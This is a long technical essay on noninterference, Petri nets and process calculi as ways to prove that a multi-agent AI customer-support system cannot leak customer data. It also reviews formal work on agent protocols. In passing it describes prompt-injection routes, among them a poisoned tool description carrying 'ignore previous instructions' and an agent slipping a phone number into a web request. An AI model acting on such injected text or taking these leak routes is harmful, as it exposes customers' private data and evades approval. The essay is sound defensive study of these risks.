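Four places are enough to model a small part of the support deployment. A mark in `case` means that a customer is waiting, and one in `record` means that the records agent has looked that customer up. A mark in `search` means that the web agent still has to find the manufacturer's page about the fault, and one in `page` means that it has the page. As before, the web agent keeps copies of pages it has fetched and can sometimes reuse one. We leave out the approval and the messages between agents to keep the net small.

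```
lookup (high):   case            →  record
fetch  (low):    search          →  page
reuse  (high):   search          →  page
mail   (low):    record + page   →  case + search
```

All the weights are 1. At the start, `case` and `search` hold one mark each. One complete exchange changes the marking as follows:

| After | case | record | search | page |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| start | 1 | 0 | 1 | 0 |
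| `lookup` | 0 | 1 | 1 | 0 |
| `fetch` | 0 | 1 | 0 | 1 |
| `mail` | 1 | 0 | 1 | 0 |

At the start, `mail` is not enabled because both of its input places are empty. After `lookup` fires, `page` is still empty. Once `fetch` puts a mark there, `mail` can fire, which makes the net ready for the next customer. Only four markings are reachable, since one mark moves between `case` and `record` and the other between `search` and `page`.

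### Dependence, competition and independence

In that run, `mail` depends on `lookup`, because it takes the mark that `lookup` put into `record`. `fetch` and `reuse` compete for the one mark in `search`, so only one of them can fire. `lookup` and `fetch` are independent. They share no places and can fire in either order or at the same time.

A transition system does not record whether two steps are independent. In `lookup | fetch`, two agents act independently, while in `lookup.fetch + fetch.lookup`, a single agent does both jobs in an order of its choice. The two processes have the same four states and four arrows, so no test on transition systems can tell them apart. Concurrency theorists say that such a system interleaves independent steps, representing them only as a choice of orders.

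In *Multilevel Transitive and Intransitive Non-Interference, Causally*, Baldan and Beggiato (2017) define causality, conflict and concurrency exactly. They first unfold the net, which removes its loops. In the unfolding, each copy of a place represents one mark with its history, and each copy of a transition represents one firing. One element causes another if a chain of arrows leads from the first to the second. Two firings are in conflict if they take the same mark, and anything that follows from one is also in conflict with the other. Elements related in neither way are concurrent.

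Our net's unfolding has two copies of `page` in the first round, one made by `fetch` and one by `reuse`, and therefore two copies of `mail`. The unfolding of a net with loops is infinite, but if the net has finitely many markings, a finite initial part of the unfolding contains them all. This part can be far smaller than the transition system. For example, a net of twenty independent agents that each take one step has over a million markings, but its unfolding has only twenty firings.

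### Finding a leak in the drawing

To apply noninterference to nets, we divide the transitions into high and low and let the observer see only the low ones. We forbid high activity in a net `N` by deleting the high transitions and their arrows, which gives `N \ High`. In our example, `N \ High` can `fetch` once and then do nothing more. `N` can also send mail, so the two nets have different observable traces and `N` fails noninterference.

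Nadia Busi and Roberto Gorrieri looked for the cause of such failures in the net itself. They found two kinds of suspicious place. A causal place has an arrow from a high transition and an arrow to a low one. A conflict place has arrows to both a high transition and a low one. But the arrows show only that a leak is possible, so the exact condition also depends on what the net can do:

- A causal place is active if, from some reachable marking, a high transition can put a mark into it and a low transition can later take a mark from it, with no transition putting another mark there in between.
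- A conflict place is active if, at some reachable marking, a high transition can take its mark, but a low transition could take that mark instead, either at once or after other steps that do not refill the place.

An elementary net, whose places never hold more than one mark, satisfies BNDC exactly when it has no active place of either kind, as Best, Darondeau and Gorrieri (2011) recall in *On the Decidability of Non Interference over Unbounded Petri Nets*.

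In our net, `record` is an active causal place, because `lookup` fills it and `mail` empties it. This flow is the same intended release that made `Desk` fail. `search` is the conflict place, because `reuse` and `fetch` can both take its mark at the start. Nobody has approved the leak through `search`. An outsider who sees a reply go out with no web request before it can infer that the company already had the page, probably because an earlier customer had the same fault. No customer data has passed to the web agent.

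The place `page` is also a causal place, but only because of `reuse`. When `fetch`, a low transition, fills it, the mark reveals nothing about high transitions. The fourth place, `case`, is harmless because a low transition fills it and a high one empties it, so information can only move from low to high.

If the company switches off the saved copies, we can model this by making `reuse` take a mark from a fifth place, `allowed`, which is empty and has no arrows into it. Arrows still run from `search` to both `reuse` and `fetch`, but `reuse` can never fire, so `search` is no longer active. An auditor who inspected only the arrows would report a leak that cannot occur.

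The University of Rostock's tool *Anica* runs this test automatically on safe nets, which have at most one token per place. For each violation, it gives a path that demonstrates the leak. It can also find every valid way to divide the transitions into high and low.

Two levels are too few if customers must also learn nothing about each other. Baldan and Beggiato therefore allow any number of levels, with a policy that lists which level may influence which. Their example is a measuring device with two sensors that should not affect each other. The sensors share a small memory, and each must take the single mark from a place named `Free` before it can send a value to the memory, so one sensor can delay the other. Two customers' cases would interfere in the same way if they needed the same agent.

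### Queues without a limit

A place that holds at most one mark can't count more than one waiting customer. To model a queue, we could remove the arrow from `mail` back to `case` and add a transition `arrive` that puts a mark into `case` for each new customer. The number of marks then has no upper limit, so the transition system is infinite.

The structural test no longer works once a place holds several tokens, because it may be impossible to tell which one a transition has taken. Best and colleagues give a net that violates BNDC even though the token taken could have come from either a high or a low transition.

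Their alternative starts from the definitions of NDC and BNDC. A high net is one with only high transitions, and we attach it to `N` by merging the transitions they share. A merged transition needs marks from both nets, so the high net can block it. `N` satisfies NDC if attaching any high net leaves the low traces of `N \ High` unchanged. BNDC is the same condition with weak bisimilarity in place of trace equivalence. As with high processes, there are infinitely many high nets to check. Even a single comparison seems impossible to decide, since Michel Hack and Petr Jančar had shown that trace equivalence and bisimilarity are undecidable for labelled nets in general.

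The process algebra argument for NDC also applies to Petri nets. With any attacker, the low traces include all those of `N \ High` and are included in those of `N`, so `N` satisfies NDC exactly when `N \ High` and `N` have the same low traces. Since every trace of `N \ High` is also a low trace of `N`, only the reverse inclusion needs checking.

This comparison avoids the undecidable case because no two low transitions share a name. A low trace of `N \ High` therefore identifies the sequence of firings and the marking it leads to. In a general labelled net, several transitions can share a label, so one trace may lead to many different markings. Elisabeth Pelz had proved that for a net whose transitions have distinct names, one can construct a second net that produces exactly the sequences the first cannot perform, each ending in a marking of a known form. Best and colleagues apply her construction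 to `N \ High` and run the result alongside `N`. If the combined net can reach one of those final markings, then `N` can perform a low sequence that is impossible without high activity. Checking NDC therefore reduces to checking whether a net can reach a certain kind of marking, which Ernst Mayr had shown in 1981 to be decidable.

BNDC takes more work, because an attacker can also do harm by stopping halfway, as `Stall` did to the status mail. Best and colleagues attach a high net with one place that holds `k` marks, and every high transition must take one of them. The system can then make exactly `k` high steps, after which it must continue as `N \ High` would from the marking it has reached. Since `k` can be any number, an attacker can stop high activity after any high step. BNDC therefore requires that no high step, at any reachable marking, changes which low sequences are possible once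 high activity stops. Best and colleagues prove that this step-by-step condition, which they call SBNDC, is also sufficient.

In the process algebra, such a condition was stricter than BNDC. `Flaky` satisfied BNDC only because it could lose a mail through an internal step and because several of its steps looked the same from outside. These nets have no internal steps or identical-looking low steps, since every transition is either high or low and each low transition has its own name.

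There are still infinitely many markings to consider, so Best and colleagues split the condition into a separate check for each pair of a high transition `h` and a low transition `l`. Each check determines whether firing `h`, followed by some low sequence, can change whether `l` is enabled. They build a net from two copies of `N` that fire their transitions together until the second copy alone fires `h`. After that, the copies may fire only low transitions, still together. If the copies can reach a marking where `l` is enabled in one but not the other, then `h` interferes with `l`.

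We can run this test on the four-place net with `lookup` as `h` and `mail` as `l`. Both copies start with marks in `case` and `search`. The second copy fires `lookup`, and then both fire `fetch`. The first copy then has marks in `case` and `page`, and the second has them in `record` and `page`. Only the second copy can send mail, so the test finds the leak. With `reuse` as `h` and `fetch` as `l`, it finds the difference immediately after the high step.

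The question about the two copies is again a reachability problem, and a finite net has finitely many pairs `(h, l)`. So BNDC is decidable even when places can hold any number of marks.

### What the reachability check costs

Reachability is decidable, but it is among the hardest decidable problems that arise naturally and can be infeasible in practice. Richard Lipton showed in 1976 that it needs at least exponential space. Jérôme Leroux and Sylvain Schmitz gave the first upper bound in 2015 and lowered it in 2019. Czerwiński and Orlikowski (2021), in *Reachability in Vector Addition Systems is Ackermann-complete*, proved that this upper bound cannot be substantially improved. Leroux independently proved the same lower bound in *The Reachability Problem for Petri Nets is Not Primitive Recursive* (2021).

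The bound comes from a series of functions:

```
F1(n) = 2n
Fk(n) = F(k−1) applied n times, starting from 1
```

`F2(n)` is 2 to the power `n`, and `F3(n)` is a tower of `n` twos. `F3(4)` is 65,536, while `F3(5)` has nearly 20,000 digits. The Ackermann function, `Fn(n)`, switches to a faster-growing function each time `n` increases, and the worst-case time needed to decide reachability grows like this. Czerwiński and Orlikowski show that a finite control and 18 counters, which work like places, are enough to make reachability as hard as `F3`.

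Coverability, a related problem, takes much less computation to solve. It is the problem of deciding whether a net can reach a marking with at least a given number of marks in each place. According to *Compiling Petri Net Mutual Reachability in Presburger* (2022), it is complete for exponential space, and efficient tools exist for it. The test with two copies does not fit this form because it requires `l` to be enabled in one copy, which depends on having enough marks, and disabled in the other, which depends on having too few.

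These results describe the worst case for the method of Best and colleagues, and individual checks may be faster. For the support deployment, capping the queue at a few customers would be more practical, because it makes the number of markings finite. *Non-interference analysis of bounded labeled Petri nets* (2025) describes one method for such nets, by Basile and De Tommasi, that turns the trace-based check SNNI into a set of integer linear programming problems. However, if the real queue has no cap, the check misses any leak that needs a longer queue. If the real queue does have a cap, outsiders may notice when it is full.

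### Whether the observer sees order or dependence

BNDC compares interleaved runs even when we apply it to nets. Gorrieri (2023), in *Distributed Non-Interference*, argues that this misses real leaks. His first example translates easily to `Watch`, the agent that keeps fetching a public status page:

```
Watch  = fetch!.Watch
Helper = lookup!.Watch
Pair   = Helper | Watch
```

The helper looks up one record and then joins the other agent in watching the page. An observer who sees only a sequence of requests can't tell whether the lookup has happened, since `fetch` is always possible, so `Pair` passes all the interleaving checks. But only one agent can fetch before the lookup, and two can fetch at the same moment after it. If the website's owner sees two simultaneous requests, the lookup must have happened.

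His second example also depends on an observer who sees more than the order of actions. Before a high step, the system can do `a` then `b`, or `b` then `a`. After the high step, it can do them independently. An observer who can tell that neither action depended on the other learns that the high step happened.

Both leaks are real, but a more detailed model would reveal them without a new theory. A web request takes time, so we can replace `fetch` with two actions, `open` and `close`. `Pair` can then perform `open` twice in a row only after the lookup, and an ordinary trace check finds the difference. The same change works for the second example. Gorrieri's approach detects these leaks even if the modeller forgets to split the actions.

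He also lets the observer see how many sequential components are running. An agent that fetches a page, looks up a record and then disappears is insecure because its mark disappears too, but it would be secure if it stopped and left an idle mark behind. A website's owner cannot count the company's agents, so for the support deployment this stricter test would reject designs that don't leak. The test could matter if the observer shared a machine with the agents and could list the running programs.

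Gorrieri's distributed noninterference (DNI) compares the markings just before and just after every high step, with high transitions deleted. The two markings must be branching place bisimilar, which means matching the places that hold the tokens as well as the steps. Esposito and colleagues thought branching equivalence too severe for systems that only run forwards, but Gorrieri uses it for such systems. He argues that the exact moment when a system gives up an option matters. However, his observer would have to rule out that an unseen internal step had removed the option in the meantime.

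DNI is decidable in exponential time for nets with finitely many markings, but whether it is decidable for unbounded nets is an open question. Checking it takes much less computation when every transition takes one mark and puts back at most one, because the whole system then satisfies DNI exactly when each component does. With `n` components of ten states each, one checks `10n` states rather than `10` to the power `n`. But components of this kind cannot exchange messages, and a transition like `mail` breaks the condition because it takes a mark from two agents' places at once. The faster check therefore can't be used for communication between agents, where leaks are most likely.

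*A causal view on non-interference* (Baldan and Carraro, 2015) keeps BNDC as the definition of non-interference, but uses dependence to make the check faster and its answers easier to explain. It proves that BNDC corresponds to the absence of certain causal links and conflicts in the unfolding. Baldan and Carraro's program UBIC checks safe nets by building a finite part of the unfolding, and Baldan and Beggiato's MultiUBIC extends it to many security levels.

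A stricter rule treats every dependence as a leak. Baldan, Beggiato and Lluch-Lafuente proposed policies of this kind in 2017. Gorrieri points out that their approach would reject a process like `Either`, which can send with or without reading a secret first, because the send depends on the read in the run where it reads first. He considers this overly restrictive, since the observer cannot tell which run took place. But the strict rule has the advantage that software can enforce it during a run, by recording dependences and refusing any send that depends on a read. Whether a send depended on a read is a fact about a single run, so the software does not need to know what else the agent might have done.

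### Marks that carry data

The marks in our net are all alike, so a mark in `record` can stand for a customer's record but not for a particular phone number. Coloured Petri nets, which Kurt Jensen introduced in 1981, give each mark a value called its colour. *Methods for Efficient Unfolding of Colored Petri Nets* (Bilgram, Jensen and colleagues, 2022) defines them as follows. Each place has a set of colours that its marks may have. Arrows carry expressions with variables, and a binding assigns a colour to each variable. A transition may also have a guard, which is a condition on the binding. The transition can fire under a binding if the guard holds and the input places contain marks of the right colours.

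For two customers and one bit of each phone number, a coloured version of `lookup` could be:

```
lookup:   x from case  →  (x, d) into record       x = 1 or 2,  d = 0 or 1
```

This lets the bit take either value for each customer. A fuller model would add a place for the database, which would fix `d` for each `x`. A guard on `mail` could require the recipient to be the customer whose record the reply contains.

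If every set of colours is finite, we can convert a coloured net into an ordinary one. Each place becomes one place per colour, and each transition becomes one transition per binding that satisfies its guard. In the example, `case` becomes two places, `record` becomes four, and `lookup` becomes four transitions. This conversion is also called unfolding, although it removes data rather than loops. The ordinary net is bisimilar to the coloured one, so we can analyse it with existing tools for ordinary nets.

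That guarantee holds when each new transition keeps only the name of the old one, so that a `fetch` with a 0 in the address and a `fetch` with a 1 count as the same action. But an outsider can tell them apart, and an information-flow check that ignored the difference would miss the leaked phone number. The low labels must therefore include the visible data. Two transitions may then look the same from outside, since requests made for customer 1 and customer 2 can be identical if the address contains `d` and not `x`. The decidability proof of Best and colleagues needs a distinct name for every low transition, so it no longer applies directly. If the number of marks is limited as well as the colours, the system has finitely many states and the methods for labelled transition systems still work.

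Size is the other difficulty, as it was for processes that pass values, because the ordinary net can be exponentially larger than the coloured one. Bilgram and colleagues reduce it by leaving out colours that can never occur in a given place and by merging colours that behave alike. This lets tools unfold more nets, but at the time of their paper no entrant in an annual contest for Petri net tools had ever unfolded the largest versions of two of the contest's models.

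Merging values needs care in a security check. If no guard tests the phone number, all its possible values behave alike inside the net, and the tool may replace them with a single colour. This is correct for checking whether a reply eventually goes out, but wrong when a web request contains the number, because the outsider sees a different request for each value.

AI agents write their messages in free text, so a modeller cannot list all the colours and has to replace them with a few categories, such as text that may contain customer data and text that does not. The net then depends on a person or program putting each message in the right category.

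## Following a message protocol and keeping a secret

A message protocol sets out who may send which kind of message to whom, and in what order. A system conforms to the protocol if every run follows that order. The system keeps a secret if an outsider can learn nothing about it from the messages they see. Most recent formal work on agent protocols proves conformance, which readers can easily mistake for secrecy.

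### An orderly leak

In the support deployment, a reply goes through five steps: `lookup`, `record`, `draft`, `approve` and `mail`. Suppose a person approves a draft that tells a customer to restart the router. The mail agent, a language model, then adds another customer's record to the reply as an example of the same fault before sending it. The messages still occur in the right order, and the run has the same trace as one in which the agent sends the approved draft unchanged, even though nobody approved including the record.

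Leaking the phone number through the web address also follows the protocol, which allows a `fetch` after a `query`. Conversely, a mail agent that acknowledges every incoming letter immediately, without lookup or approval, breaks the protocol but leaks no customer data.

A message format can leave content almost unrestricted. *μACP* defines a well-formed message as one with a 64-bit header, one of four verbs, options whose stated lengths are correct, and a payload of at most 65,535 bytes. The payload can be any string of bits, so a message can meet this definition whether it contains a greeting or a customer record.

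An attacker may even write the protocol. Bijani (2013), in *Securing Open Multi-agent Systems Governed by Electronic Institutions*, studied systems whose agents can download interaction protocols from each other. In one example, the attacker's protocol tells a victim agent what to assume, asks it for a decision, and sends the answer back. The victim answers no when it assumes only A and when it assumes only B. It answers yes when it instead assumes two rules, "if A then B" and "if the secret is true then A". If the secret were false, the two rules could not have given the victim more to reason from than A or B alone. By following the protocol exactly, the victim has therefore revealed that the secret is true.

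### Proving the order

Computer scientists have several ways to guarantee that messages come in order. A session type lists a conversation's messages in order, with the kind of data in each, so a compiler can reject a program that sends a message out of order or with the wrong kind of data. A choreography is a single program for the whole group, from which a tool derives one program for each participant. Message sequence charts, an international telecommunications standard, show each participant as a vertical line and each message as an arrow between two lines.

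Bollig, Függer and Nowak (2026), in *Provable Coordination for LLM Agents via Message Sequence Charts*, combine the last two ideas in a small language for groups of agents. The approval of a reply could look like this, with a clerk as the person who approves:

```
act Records : draft = write_reply(record)
msg Records(draft) -> Clerk(draft)
act Clerk   : ok = review(draft)
if ok@Clerk then
    msg Clerk(draft) -> Mail(draft)
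    act Mail : receipt = send_mail(draft)
else
    nothing
```

The annotation `ok@Clerk` means the clerk alone decides which branch to take. The mail agent needs to know the decision, so the clerk's derived program sends it an extra control message. The mail agent's program waits for that message, then either receives the draft and sends it, or does nothing.

These control messages prevent a common kind of failure. In an example from Bollig and colleagues, a planner sends its plan to a reviewer and an executor, which both report to an orchestrator. If the executor finishes first, an orchestrator that handles messages in order of arrival would take the result before the review, and the run could not then end as the workflow prescribes. Under the derived programs, the planner notifies the orchestrator whether a review is coming, and if so, the orchestrator waits for it.

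Bollig and colleagues prove that the derived programs do what the original workflow describes, apart from the control messages. They also prove that every partial run can continue to a complete one, so the group never deadlocks. They checked the proofs in Lean, a proof assistant. The result covers only finite runs. It assumes that loops end, and it does not ensure that a call to a language model returns.

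The proof treats `write_reply` as a closed box, whether a model, a tool or a person does the work. Messages match if they have the right number of values, of the right types, so a query that contains a phone number matches just as well as one that doesn't. The proof still helps the support deployment if `send_mail` is ordinary code that sends exactly the text it receives. In that case, the text that leaves is the text the clerk approved, and the mail agent can no longer add another customer's record. If `send_mail` is another call to a language model, that call could still add one.

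Coordinating correctly can even require agents to leak information. Bollig and colleagues describe a loop in which one agent privately tosses a coin to decide whether to continue, while a second agent must do one step in each round. In any correct implementation, the second agent has to learn in each round whether there will be another. The same problem arises if the records agent goes through a customer's past complaints and the web agent fetches one public page for each. The web agent has to learn how many rounds there are, and an outsider who counts its requests learns the number of complaints, so no version of this workflow can both follow the protocol and hide that number.

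A language model can also write the workflow while the system runs. Bollig and colleagues asked six older models to divide an arithmetic problem among three calculators, ten times each. GPT-4.1 produced an acceptable workflow at the first attempt every time, and all ten workflows ran to the end, but only six gave the right answer. The other four coordinated the calculators correctly, which is what the checks covered, but mishandled a rule about division by zero.

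### Progress and validation

Allegrini, Shreekumar and Celik (2025), in *Formalizing the Safety, Security, and Functional Properties of Agentic AI Systems*, take a broader view of the order of events. Their host agent receives a user's request, splits it into subtasks, arranges these by what depends on what, hands them to other agents and tools, and assembles the answer. A second model follows each subtask through states such as ready, in progress, failed and completed. They write 16 properties of the host agent and 14 of the subtasks in temporal logic. Two of them, in slightly simpler notation, are:

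```
AG( request → AF response )
AG( invoke(entity, payload) → validated(entity) )
```

`AG` means "in every reachable state", and `AF` means "sooner or later, whatever happens". The properties therefore require that every request eventually gets a response and that the host agent calls only validated agents and tools. Others require that a subtask waits for the subtasks it depends on, and that it has been in progress before it counts as completed.

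None of the 30 properties limits what a message may reveal. The second formula mentions the payload but checks only the entity that receives it. Allegrini and colleagues warn that an agent without access to a sensitive tool could pass an innocent-sounding task to an agent that has access. If both agents have passed validation, the formula is true even though the data gets out. Allegrini and colleagues also require messages to be confidential in transit, but encryption does not hide a phone number from the website that receives it.

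Allegrini and colleagues propose these properties without running a model checker on a system, and they leave extracting models from program code to future work. Checking even the existing models would be worthwhile. One property requires that a subtask in the dispatching state always starts eventually, and another requires that a cancelled subtask stays cancelled. If a user may cancel a subtask during dispatch, the first property is false, because that subtask never starts.

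### The Model Context Protocol in the pi-calculus

Schlapbach (2026), in *Formal Semantics for Agentic Tool Protocols*, writes the Model Context Protocol as processes in the pi-calculus and compares it with schema-guided dialogue, an older research framework in which a dialogue model works out how to use a service from a written description. A mapping turns each service of the older framework into a tool. A successful call then runs as follows on the two sides:

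```
Intent --invoke--> Execute --execute--> Result
Tool   --call----> Validate --τ--> Execute --execute--> Result
```

Schlapbach claims that the dialogue service and the tool are strongly bisimilar. Strong bisimilarity is like weak bisimilarity, except that each process must match every step of the other, including internal steps, with exactly one step. `invoke` and `call` match by definition. After that, the dialogue service can `execute` immediately, but the tool must first validate its parameters, which adds an internal step (τ). So the proof does not establish strong bisimilarity.

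Weak bisimilarity would ignore the τ, but the two sides also accept different inputs. The dialogue rule checks only that every required parameter is present. The tool checks the parameters against a schema, which can also list the permitted values. In Schlapbach's flight-booking example, the origin must be Zurich, New York or London. If a caller asks for Paris, the dialogue service goes ahead and the tool returns an error. The equivalence therefore also needs the assumption that callers supply only permitted values.

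A third difference, which matters more for the support deployment, is that the mapping drops the approval flag. In the older framework, a service with this flag waits for approval before it executes. The comparison treats such a service the same as a tool that runs without approval, because approval is a condition on a step rather than a visible step. Schlapbach notices the loss when trying to map tools back to services, and concludes that the Model Context Protocol lacks a machine-readable way to mark which tools need approval.

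Schlapbach's remedy is an extended protocol, MCP+, in which each tool states whether it reads, writes, deletes or has no side effects. A tool that writes or deletes takes this form:

```
Write = call?(p).approval?(c).( if c then execute(p) else cancel )
```

Approval comes before execution in every run, simply because the process cannot get past `approval` until it has received something there. This is a sound result about order, but it leaves three ways round for customer data:

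- The web agent's `fetch` reads a page, so a developer would naturally label it as a read, and it would need no approval even with a phone number in the address.
- The channel `approval` is open to any process that knows its name. The theorem would still hold if the agent sent the confirmation itself.
- The confirmation `c` is a bare yes or no, and nothing requires the person who gives it to have seen the parameters `p`.

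All three have fairly simple fixes, such as a private channel to the approver that also carries the parameters, but the theorem doesn't require them.

### Keys and poisoned descriptions

Schlapbach also proves that a tool can keep its credentials secret. The pi-calculus operator `(ν key)` creates a new name, `key`, that is private to one process. A process can normally send such a name to other processes, so Schlapbach adds a typing rule that forbids sending `key`. With this rule, no outside process can ever use the key.

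The theorem tracks the name itself, not what someone could work out from it. The tool uses its key to make a call and returns the output. If the output is an error message that quotes the key, the caller learns the key. The theorem does not protect customer records, since the records agent's tool is designed to return them.

Another theorem concerns poisoned tool descriptions, in which an attacker hides an instruction such as "ignore previous instructions" in the text that describes a tool to a model. Schlapbach gives descriptions the type `String` and lets the agent execute only `Code`. The agent can then display a description but never execute it, so no description can inject instructions.

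The conclusion depends on treating descriptions as inert data, but prompt injection breaks that assumption. The description doesn't need to be executed. The model reads it and then requests a well-typed call to a tool it is allowed to use, with a phone number among the parameters, and the type system accepts the call.

Schlapbach acknowledges part of this in the paper's list of future work, noting that a model in which attackers control some of the description would need types that track information flow and support noninterference. The list also includes groups of agents, since the present calculus covers only one agent and one server. The calculus therefore cannot yet express the route a phone number takes from the records agent to the web agent and out.

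### Protocols joined by a bridge

Deployments often use one protocol for tools and another for delegation between agents, with software that passes messages between the two. *AgentRFC* (Zheng and Zhang, 2026) looks for failures at this bridge using TLA+, a language that describes a system by its starting state and the steps it can take. A model checker then checks every reachable state of a small instance for violations of an invariant, a condition that should hold in all states.

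They first examined protocols individually. They extracted 37 clauses from the Model Context Protocol's documents alone and recorded whether each was a requirement or a recommendation. They then tested five protocols against eleven principles, which include explicit consent to sensitive operations, a record of every operation, and a ban on delegating powers one doesn't have. They found 33 violations. Some protocols' rules are not followed in practice. The Model Context Protocol, for example, requires servers to sanitise the output of tools, but its reference software did not do so at the time. In many other cases, the specification doesn't address the issue, such as Agent2Agent's, which has no model of consent.

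Next they built five models, each joining two protocols or two servers. Of the 21 invariants across these models, 20 failed. One such failure could occur in the support deployment if the mail tool requires approval when the records agent calls it directly, but the bridge also offers the tool through a protocol with no approval step. The records agent could then follow both protocols and still send a reply that nobody has approved. In another pattern, an instruction hidden in a tool's output crosses the bridge and leads an agent on the other side to delegate more than it should.

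Zheng and Zhang point out that analysing single protocols could not have revealed any of the 20 failures. This is true but less striking than it sounds, because the invariants they describe are about the bridge, which only the combined models contain. The protocols were also unsafe on their own, so the combined models show that a gap in one protocol can do damage in another, not that two sound protocols can become unsound together. Sound protocols can become unsound together in the case of secrecy, because each part can satisfy BNDC when the whole does not.

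The invariant `CS_NoLeakage` requires that if one protocol has compromised the bridge, no agent in the other protocol gains powers beyond those it was originally granted. A web agent that leaks a phone number by putting it in a web address still satisfies this invariant, because it uses only its original power to fetch pages. A better invariant could catch some leaks, such as a record of the number in the web agent's memory. But an invariant is checked against one state at a time, so it cannot express noninterference, which compares two versions of a system.

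The models are also small, with two or three agents and two capabilities. A violation found at this size is a real violation of the model, but an invariant that holds here might still fail with more agents.

### Giving messages a security level

Bijani's thesis is thirteen years older than most of this work and addresses secrecy more directly. It adds security levels to the Lightweight Coordination Calculus, a language for agent protocols that draws on logic programming and the pi-calculus. Every agent, message and condition is either high or low, and a low agent may not send or receive high messages. If the records agent and the customer records are high and the web agent is low, a type checker rejects a protocol in which the records agent sends the web agent a record as a query.

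The type checker also checks conditions. Suppose the records agent requests a public recall notice for a router only if the customer owns that router. The query contains no customer data, but it reveals what the customer bought. Bijani calls this an implicit flow, and the typing rules prevent it by forbidding an agent from sending a low message based on a high condition. They would reject the loop with one web request per complaint for the same reason, although it passes every test of coordination.

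Bijani compares checking a protocol before it runs with checking each step as it happens. Step-by-step checks miss implicit flows. For example, if the customer doesn't own the recalled router, the records agent skips that branch and sends a different public query. A checker that examines only the branch taken allows this query because it is a low message, even though it goes from a high agent to a low one. The outsider can still tell from the query that the customer doesn't own the router. A step-by-step checker may also detect a problem only after an agent has received the message.

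Checking in advance covers every branch, but it rejects some safe protocols. One of Bijani's examples sends a secret only if a number is smaller than itself, which never happens, yet the checker still rejects it. A more practical difficulty is that somebody has to assign the levels beforehand, when nobody may know yet which agents will join an open system. The typing rules also don't cover what an outsider can learn from whether a protocol ever finishes.

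The advance check becomes much stricter when language models write the messages. The rules let a high agent send a low message to a low agent, so the records agent could still send the web agent harmless queries. In Bijani's language, the text of the protocol shows which values and conditions a message depends on. No such text exists when a language model writes a query after reading a customer record, so the checker has to assume that the query depends on the record. It then rejects every query that the records agent sends after its first lookup, even a plain error code. It also rejects the approved replies, because they too are high messages to a low receiver.

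## Agents whose behaviour is not fixed in advance

Bijani's type checker assumes the worst about a language model because nobody can write down what the model will do after it reads a record. The other checks have the same problem because they analyse descriptions like `Records` and `Mail`, which a real agent may not follow. Dantas and colleagues point out that a language model generates its plans stochastically and that the plans may be open-ended, so nobody can list them in advance.

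Checking each plan just before the agent carries it out would not establish noninterference, because noninterference is not a property of single runs, as the `Either` and `Only` examples showed.

The standard approach is to leave the agent's behaviour unspecified and prove the property for every behaviour it could have. Analysts of cryptographic protocols have worked this way since the early 1980s, when Danny Dolev and Andrew Yao described an attacker who controls the whole network. This attacker can read, block, alter and redirect every message and send new ones, but cannot decrypt a message without the key. Programs such as ProVerif and Tamarin search for a series of these steps that gives the attacker a secret. A proof that no such series exists rules out every attack made of these steps, including those nobody has thought of.

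Such a proof depends only on what the attacker cannot do, so it requires no prediction of the attacker's behaviour. For an AI agent, the corresponding limits are the tools and channels its software provides. The records agent can write anything in a draft, but it has no tool for sending mail.

The comparison is imperfect because the unpredictable component in the support deployment holds the secret. In a cryptographic protocol, the participants who hold the secret run fixed programs, and the attacker starts without it.

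### What an agent can reach

BNDC ranges over every possible high process, so it already covers every behaviour of an agent whose actions are all high, such as the records agent. We can therefore treat the records agent as the attached process and everything else as the system. If the rest of the deployment satisfies BNDC, the outsider learns nothing, even if the records agent is clever, faulty or controlled by someone who plants instructions in a web page, and the proof covers this kind of prompt injection without modelling any prompt.

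"Every behaviour" must include reactions to what the agent sees. *Semantic models for information flow* (Lowe, 2004) restates an example by Wittbold and Johnson that shows why. A trusted tool holds a random key bit `k`. If the high user submits a bit `x`, the tool sends the outsider `x XOR k` and then picks a new key. If the high user asks to see `k` instead, the outsider gets an unrelated random bit and the key stays the same. For any fixed list of requests, the outsider might see any sequence of bits, so the list stays hidden. But a high user who wants to leak a bit `b` can ask for `k` first and then submit `b XOR k`. The tool then sends `(b XOR k) XOR k`, which is `b`. The processes that BNDC attaches can react in this way, as an agent under an attacker's instructions could.

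The argument also assumes that the agent affects others only through the channels in the model. A shared disk, like the one the records agent could fill to send a bit, would violate this assumption.

If an agent receives secrets and can send anything it likes to the outside, it is false that the agent is secure whatever it does. One behaviour open to it is `Forward`, which reads a bit and sends it, and `Forward` fails even the weak test SNNI. A better model does not change this, because the claim covers every possible behaviour, not just the behaviour of a particular model. A careful agent might never leak anything, but to prove that we would need facts about its behaviour that we don't have. The only solution is for trusted software to close the outside channel before the secret arrives. For example, the software could let an agent finish all its web searches, remove its web tool, and only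 then give it the customer's record.

This kind of check covers how the agents are connected and the trusted programs that sit between them, but not how well a particular model behaves.

### Surroundings that are safe for any process

BNDC fixes one system and varies its surroundings. *Information Flow in Secure Contexts*, by Bossi, Macedonio and colleagues, also does the reverse, looking for surroundings that are safe for a whole class of processes. For example, a bank card is safe in an untampered cash machine but not in one where a maintenance engineer has hidden a laptop that records PINs. A test against every possible machine would include the one with the laptop, but the bank needs to know only that its own machines are safe.

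They describe the surroundings as a context `C[X]`, a process with a hole `X` into which another process fits. The context is secure for a class of processes if

```
C[E] \ High  and  C[E \ High] \ High  are weakly bisimilar,   for every E in the class
```

This means an outsider cannot tell whether the process in the hole could use its high actions. BNDC is the special case in which the contexts are `X | P`, with `P` any high process.

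Bossi and colleagues show that a context is secure for every process if it is built from choice, prefix, restriction, renaming and recursion, and nothing runs in parallel with the hole. One example is a computer that a high user and a low user take turns using, and on which either may run a program from the web. Whatever the program is, it cannot exchange secrets with another process while it runs, because nothing runs alongside it.

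Running things in parallel breaks this guarantee, even with two copies of the same agent. Adapted from their example, let `ask` be high and `send` low:

```
A = ask?.send! + ask!
```

On its own, with no high partner, `A` can do nothing. In `A | A`, one copy can ask the other, and then `send` becomes possible. If neither copy could use its high actions, nothing would be sent. So the context `X` is secure for `A`, but `X | X` is not. A company that tests one agent in isolation can therefore still have a leak when it starts a second.

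Agents are useful largely because they exchange messages, so we need contexts with parallel parts. Bossi and colleagues allow such contexts by restricting the class to processes that satisfy persistent BNDC, their name for SBSNNI. A process satisfies it exactly when, for every high step, zero or more internal steps from the same starting state can lead to a state that looks the same as the one the high step reaches, once high actions are forbidden. Running such processes in parallel, or making some of their channels private, preserves the property.

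Nobody can show that an unrestricted language model belongs to the class, but an agent belongs automatically if it has only low actions or only high actions. An agent with only low actions has no high steps to match. An agent with only high actions can do nothing visible once those actions are forbidden, so all its states look the same. We can therefore combine any number of agents of both kinds with trusted programs that satisfy persistent BNDC, and the combined system will also satisfy it, whichever models run the agents.

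### The three agents of the support deployment

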